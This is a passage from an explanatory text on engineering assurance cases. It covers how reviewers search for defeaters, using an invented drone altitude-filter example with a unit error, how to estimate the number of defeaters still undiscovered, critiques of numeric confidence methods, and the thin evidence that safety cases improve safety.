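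Developers record each defeater and how they resolved it, so that later reviewers don't have to think of the same objection again. They aim for an indefeasible case, in which they have searched for defeaters so thoroughly that no credible new information would change the decision. In practice they can only work towards this standard, because nobody can list everything that might be discovered.

### Reviewing a case for one filter

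Suppose engineers insert a filter between a drone's flight planner and its waypoint manager. The filter should block any plan with an altitude outside 100 to 1,000 metres. In this invented example, the first draft of the case looks like this:

- Claim C1: Every plan that reaches the waypoint manager stays between 100 and 1,000 metres.
  - Claim C2: Every plan that reaches the waypoint manager has passed through the filter.
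    - Evidence: Trace of every connection
  - Claim C3: The filter passes only plans that stay between 100 and 1,000 metres.
    - Evidence: Proof that the filter's code meets its contract

The reviewers start with the reasoning and find that C2 and C3 don't make C1 certain, because something could alter a plan after the filter has approved it. The developers add claim C4, that nothing alters a plan between the filter and the waypoint manager, and support it by checking the connection between them. C1 now follows from C2, C3 and C4.

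Next, the reviewers look for defeaters in the evidence. Links between documents may be missing or wrong, and a formal model may be too abstract to reveal a real defect. Both suggestions come from another of Bloomfield's experiments with language models.

| Defeater | Check | Finding | Resolution |
|---|---|---|---|
| D1: The proof covers a different version of the filter from the one on the drone | Compare a digital fingerprint of the installed program with the one in the proof record | They match | Rejected, with the comparison added to C3's evidence |
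| D2: The contract treats altitude as a bare number, so the planner may use different units | Read the planner's interface document and a recorded plan | The planner sends feet | Upheld, so engineers make the filter convert feet to metres, add units to the contract and rerun the proof |

D2 is serious because the original filter would read a plan at 300 feet as 300 metres and pass it, although 300 feet is only about 91 metres. It would also block a good plan at 2,000 feet, or 610 metres. The original proof was valid, but it was about numbers rather than the heights they represented. After the repair, engineers should also test that the filter blocks a 300-foot plan.

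The repair reopens D1 because the program on the drone is now out of date. D1 stays open until the engineers install the new version and compare the fingerprints again. The developers also record that the proof tool may contain a bug. They might accept this remaining doubt because tests with plans just outside the limits would probably expose a large error.

### How many defeaters are left?

Bloomfield tried a method that biologists use to estimate fish populations. They tag and release one catch, then count the tagged fish in a second catch. If two reviewers find *n*₁ and *n*₂ defeaters, with *m* in common, the estimated total is *n*₁ × *n*₂ / *m*. For example, if they find 20 and 15 with 10 in common, the estimated total is 30. Together they have found 25 different defeaters, so about five remain.

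In Bloomfield's experiment, ChatGPT and Gemini Pro acted as reviewers, and each listed defeaters for claims from an engineering project's report. Each list had about 40 defeaters, which gave an estimated total of roughly 70. Bloomfield calls this speculative. The formula assumes that the reviewers search independently, but language models are trained on much of the same text. If they tend to miss the same defeaters, their lists overlap more and the estimate is too low.

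The count also gives every defeater equal weight. The models identified the general category of the defeater Bloomfield considered most important but missed the defeater itself. Bloomfield also warns that reading long lists of plausible objections can replace thinking.

### Putting a number on confidence

Someone who has to approve a system might prefer a single number, such as "92% confident that it is safe". Graydon and Holloway (2016), in *An Investigation of Proposed Techniques for Quantifying Confidence in Assurance Arguments*, examined 12 methods for calculating such a number. They changed a few details in the inventors' published examples and checked whether the answers still made sense. Nine of the methods gave an implausible answer in at least one case. The other three had no worked example that Graydon and Holloway could reproduce or adapt.

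One method rates how sufficient the evidence is, how insufficient it is and how much uncertainty remains, then combines these ratings from the lower claims up to the top claim. A claim is acceptable if its sufficiency rating is well above its uncertainty rating. Graydon and Holloway applied the method to an argument that the developers had dealt with 21 hazards.

| Version of the argument | Sufficiency of top claim | Uncertainty |
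|---|---|---|
| 21 hazards, with good evidence for each | 0.801 | 0.099 |
| 21 hazards, with almost no support for one | 0.765 | 0.096 |
| The same system and evidence, with 19 of the hazards merged into one | 0.079 | 0.868 |

In the second row, one hazard may be completely uncontrolled, but the result barely changes because the evidence about the others is good. A single uncontrolled hazard was enough to destroy XV230. The third row describes the same system as the second, but it is now rejected because somebody grouped the hazards differently.

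Another method gave 90.0% confidence in a system's safety when analysts were 99.9% confident that their hazard list was complete, and still gave 86.4% when they were only 0.1% confident.

Better formulas might avoid some of these results, but they would still need trustworthy inputs. Nobody has good data on how strongly each kind of evidence supports each kind of claim, so the methods rely on expert guesses. Few of the papers give a rule for using the answer, so a reader can't tell whether an answer of 80% is enough to put a system into service.

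The methods had also received little testing. In the only experiment, 31 master's students rated arguments on a five-point scale. The method's answers differed from the students' by about one point, roughly as much as the students differed from their own earlier answers. That is encouraging, but the researchers apparently used the same data to tune and test the method. The only survey asked 21 safety experts whether one method would make assessments more accurate. Thirteen agreed, but they had only seen a presentation about it.

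Graydon and Holloway argue that nobody has shown the methods' answers to be good enough for deciding whether to use a critical system. They don't claim that the underlying probability theories are wrong, or that the methods usually give bad answers.

Bloomfield and Rushby still calculate probabilities, but only for cases whose reasoning and evidence have already passed review. This review doesn't supply the missing data, but it prevents the masking shown in the table, because a claim about 21 hazards fails if the evidence for any one of them is inadequate.

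### Do assurance cases improve safety?

The empirical evidence that safety cases make systems safer is weak. Habli, Alexander and Hawkins, who work on safety cases themselves, found very little research on whether the practice as a whole has this effect. The main study, which Rinehart, Knight and Rowanhill wrote for NASA in 2017, relies on published literature and interviews with practitioners about their own experience. In their view, reports about large projects that used safety cases successfully are little more than detailed anecdotes. The fall in British offshore accidents after Piper Alpha is stronger evidence, but other changes may explain part of the fall.

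People also draw different lessons from the Nimrod accident. The MIT Energy Initiative's *Risk management in the oil and gas industry* describes the Review as citing safety cases as a major contributor to the accident. Haddon-Cave did call the ministry's safety case system ineffective and wasteful, but the Review also concluded that a competent safety case would have saved the aircraft. One accident isn't enough evidence to determine whether a typical safety case does more good than harm.

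A better study would have to compare safety cases with other ways of spending the same money, such as following detailed standards. That is difficult because serious accidents are rare, companies keep their safety cases confidential, and few managers would pay to assure the same system twice.

Habli, Alexander and Hawkins outline a possible study of aircraft software that would compare a GSN safety case, a table of hazards and the records that DO-178C requires. Researchers would ask engineers how well they understood the ways software failures could contribute to hazards, then count software-related safety incidents over five years.

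They suggest that a more rigorous argument might make very little difference for a conventional wheel-braking system but reduce incidents for an aircraft that taxis by itself. The study would be expensive, and they aren't sure industry would fund it. They consider case studies inside companies more practical, and also want researchers to test some theories that are quite critical of safety cases.
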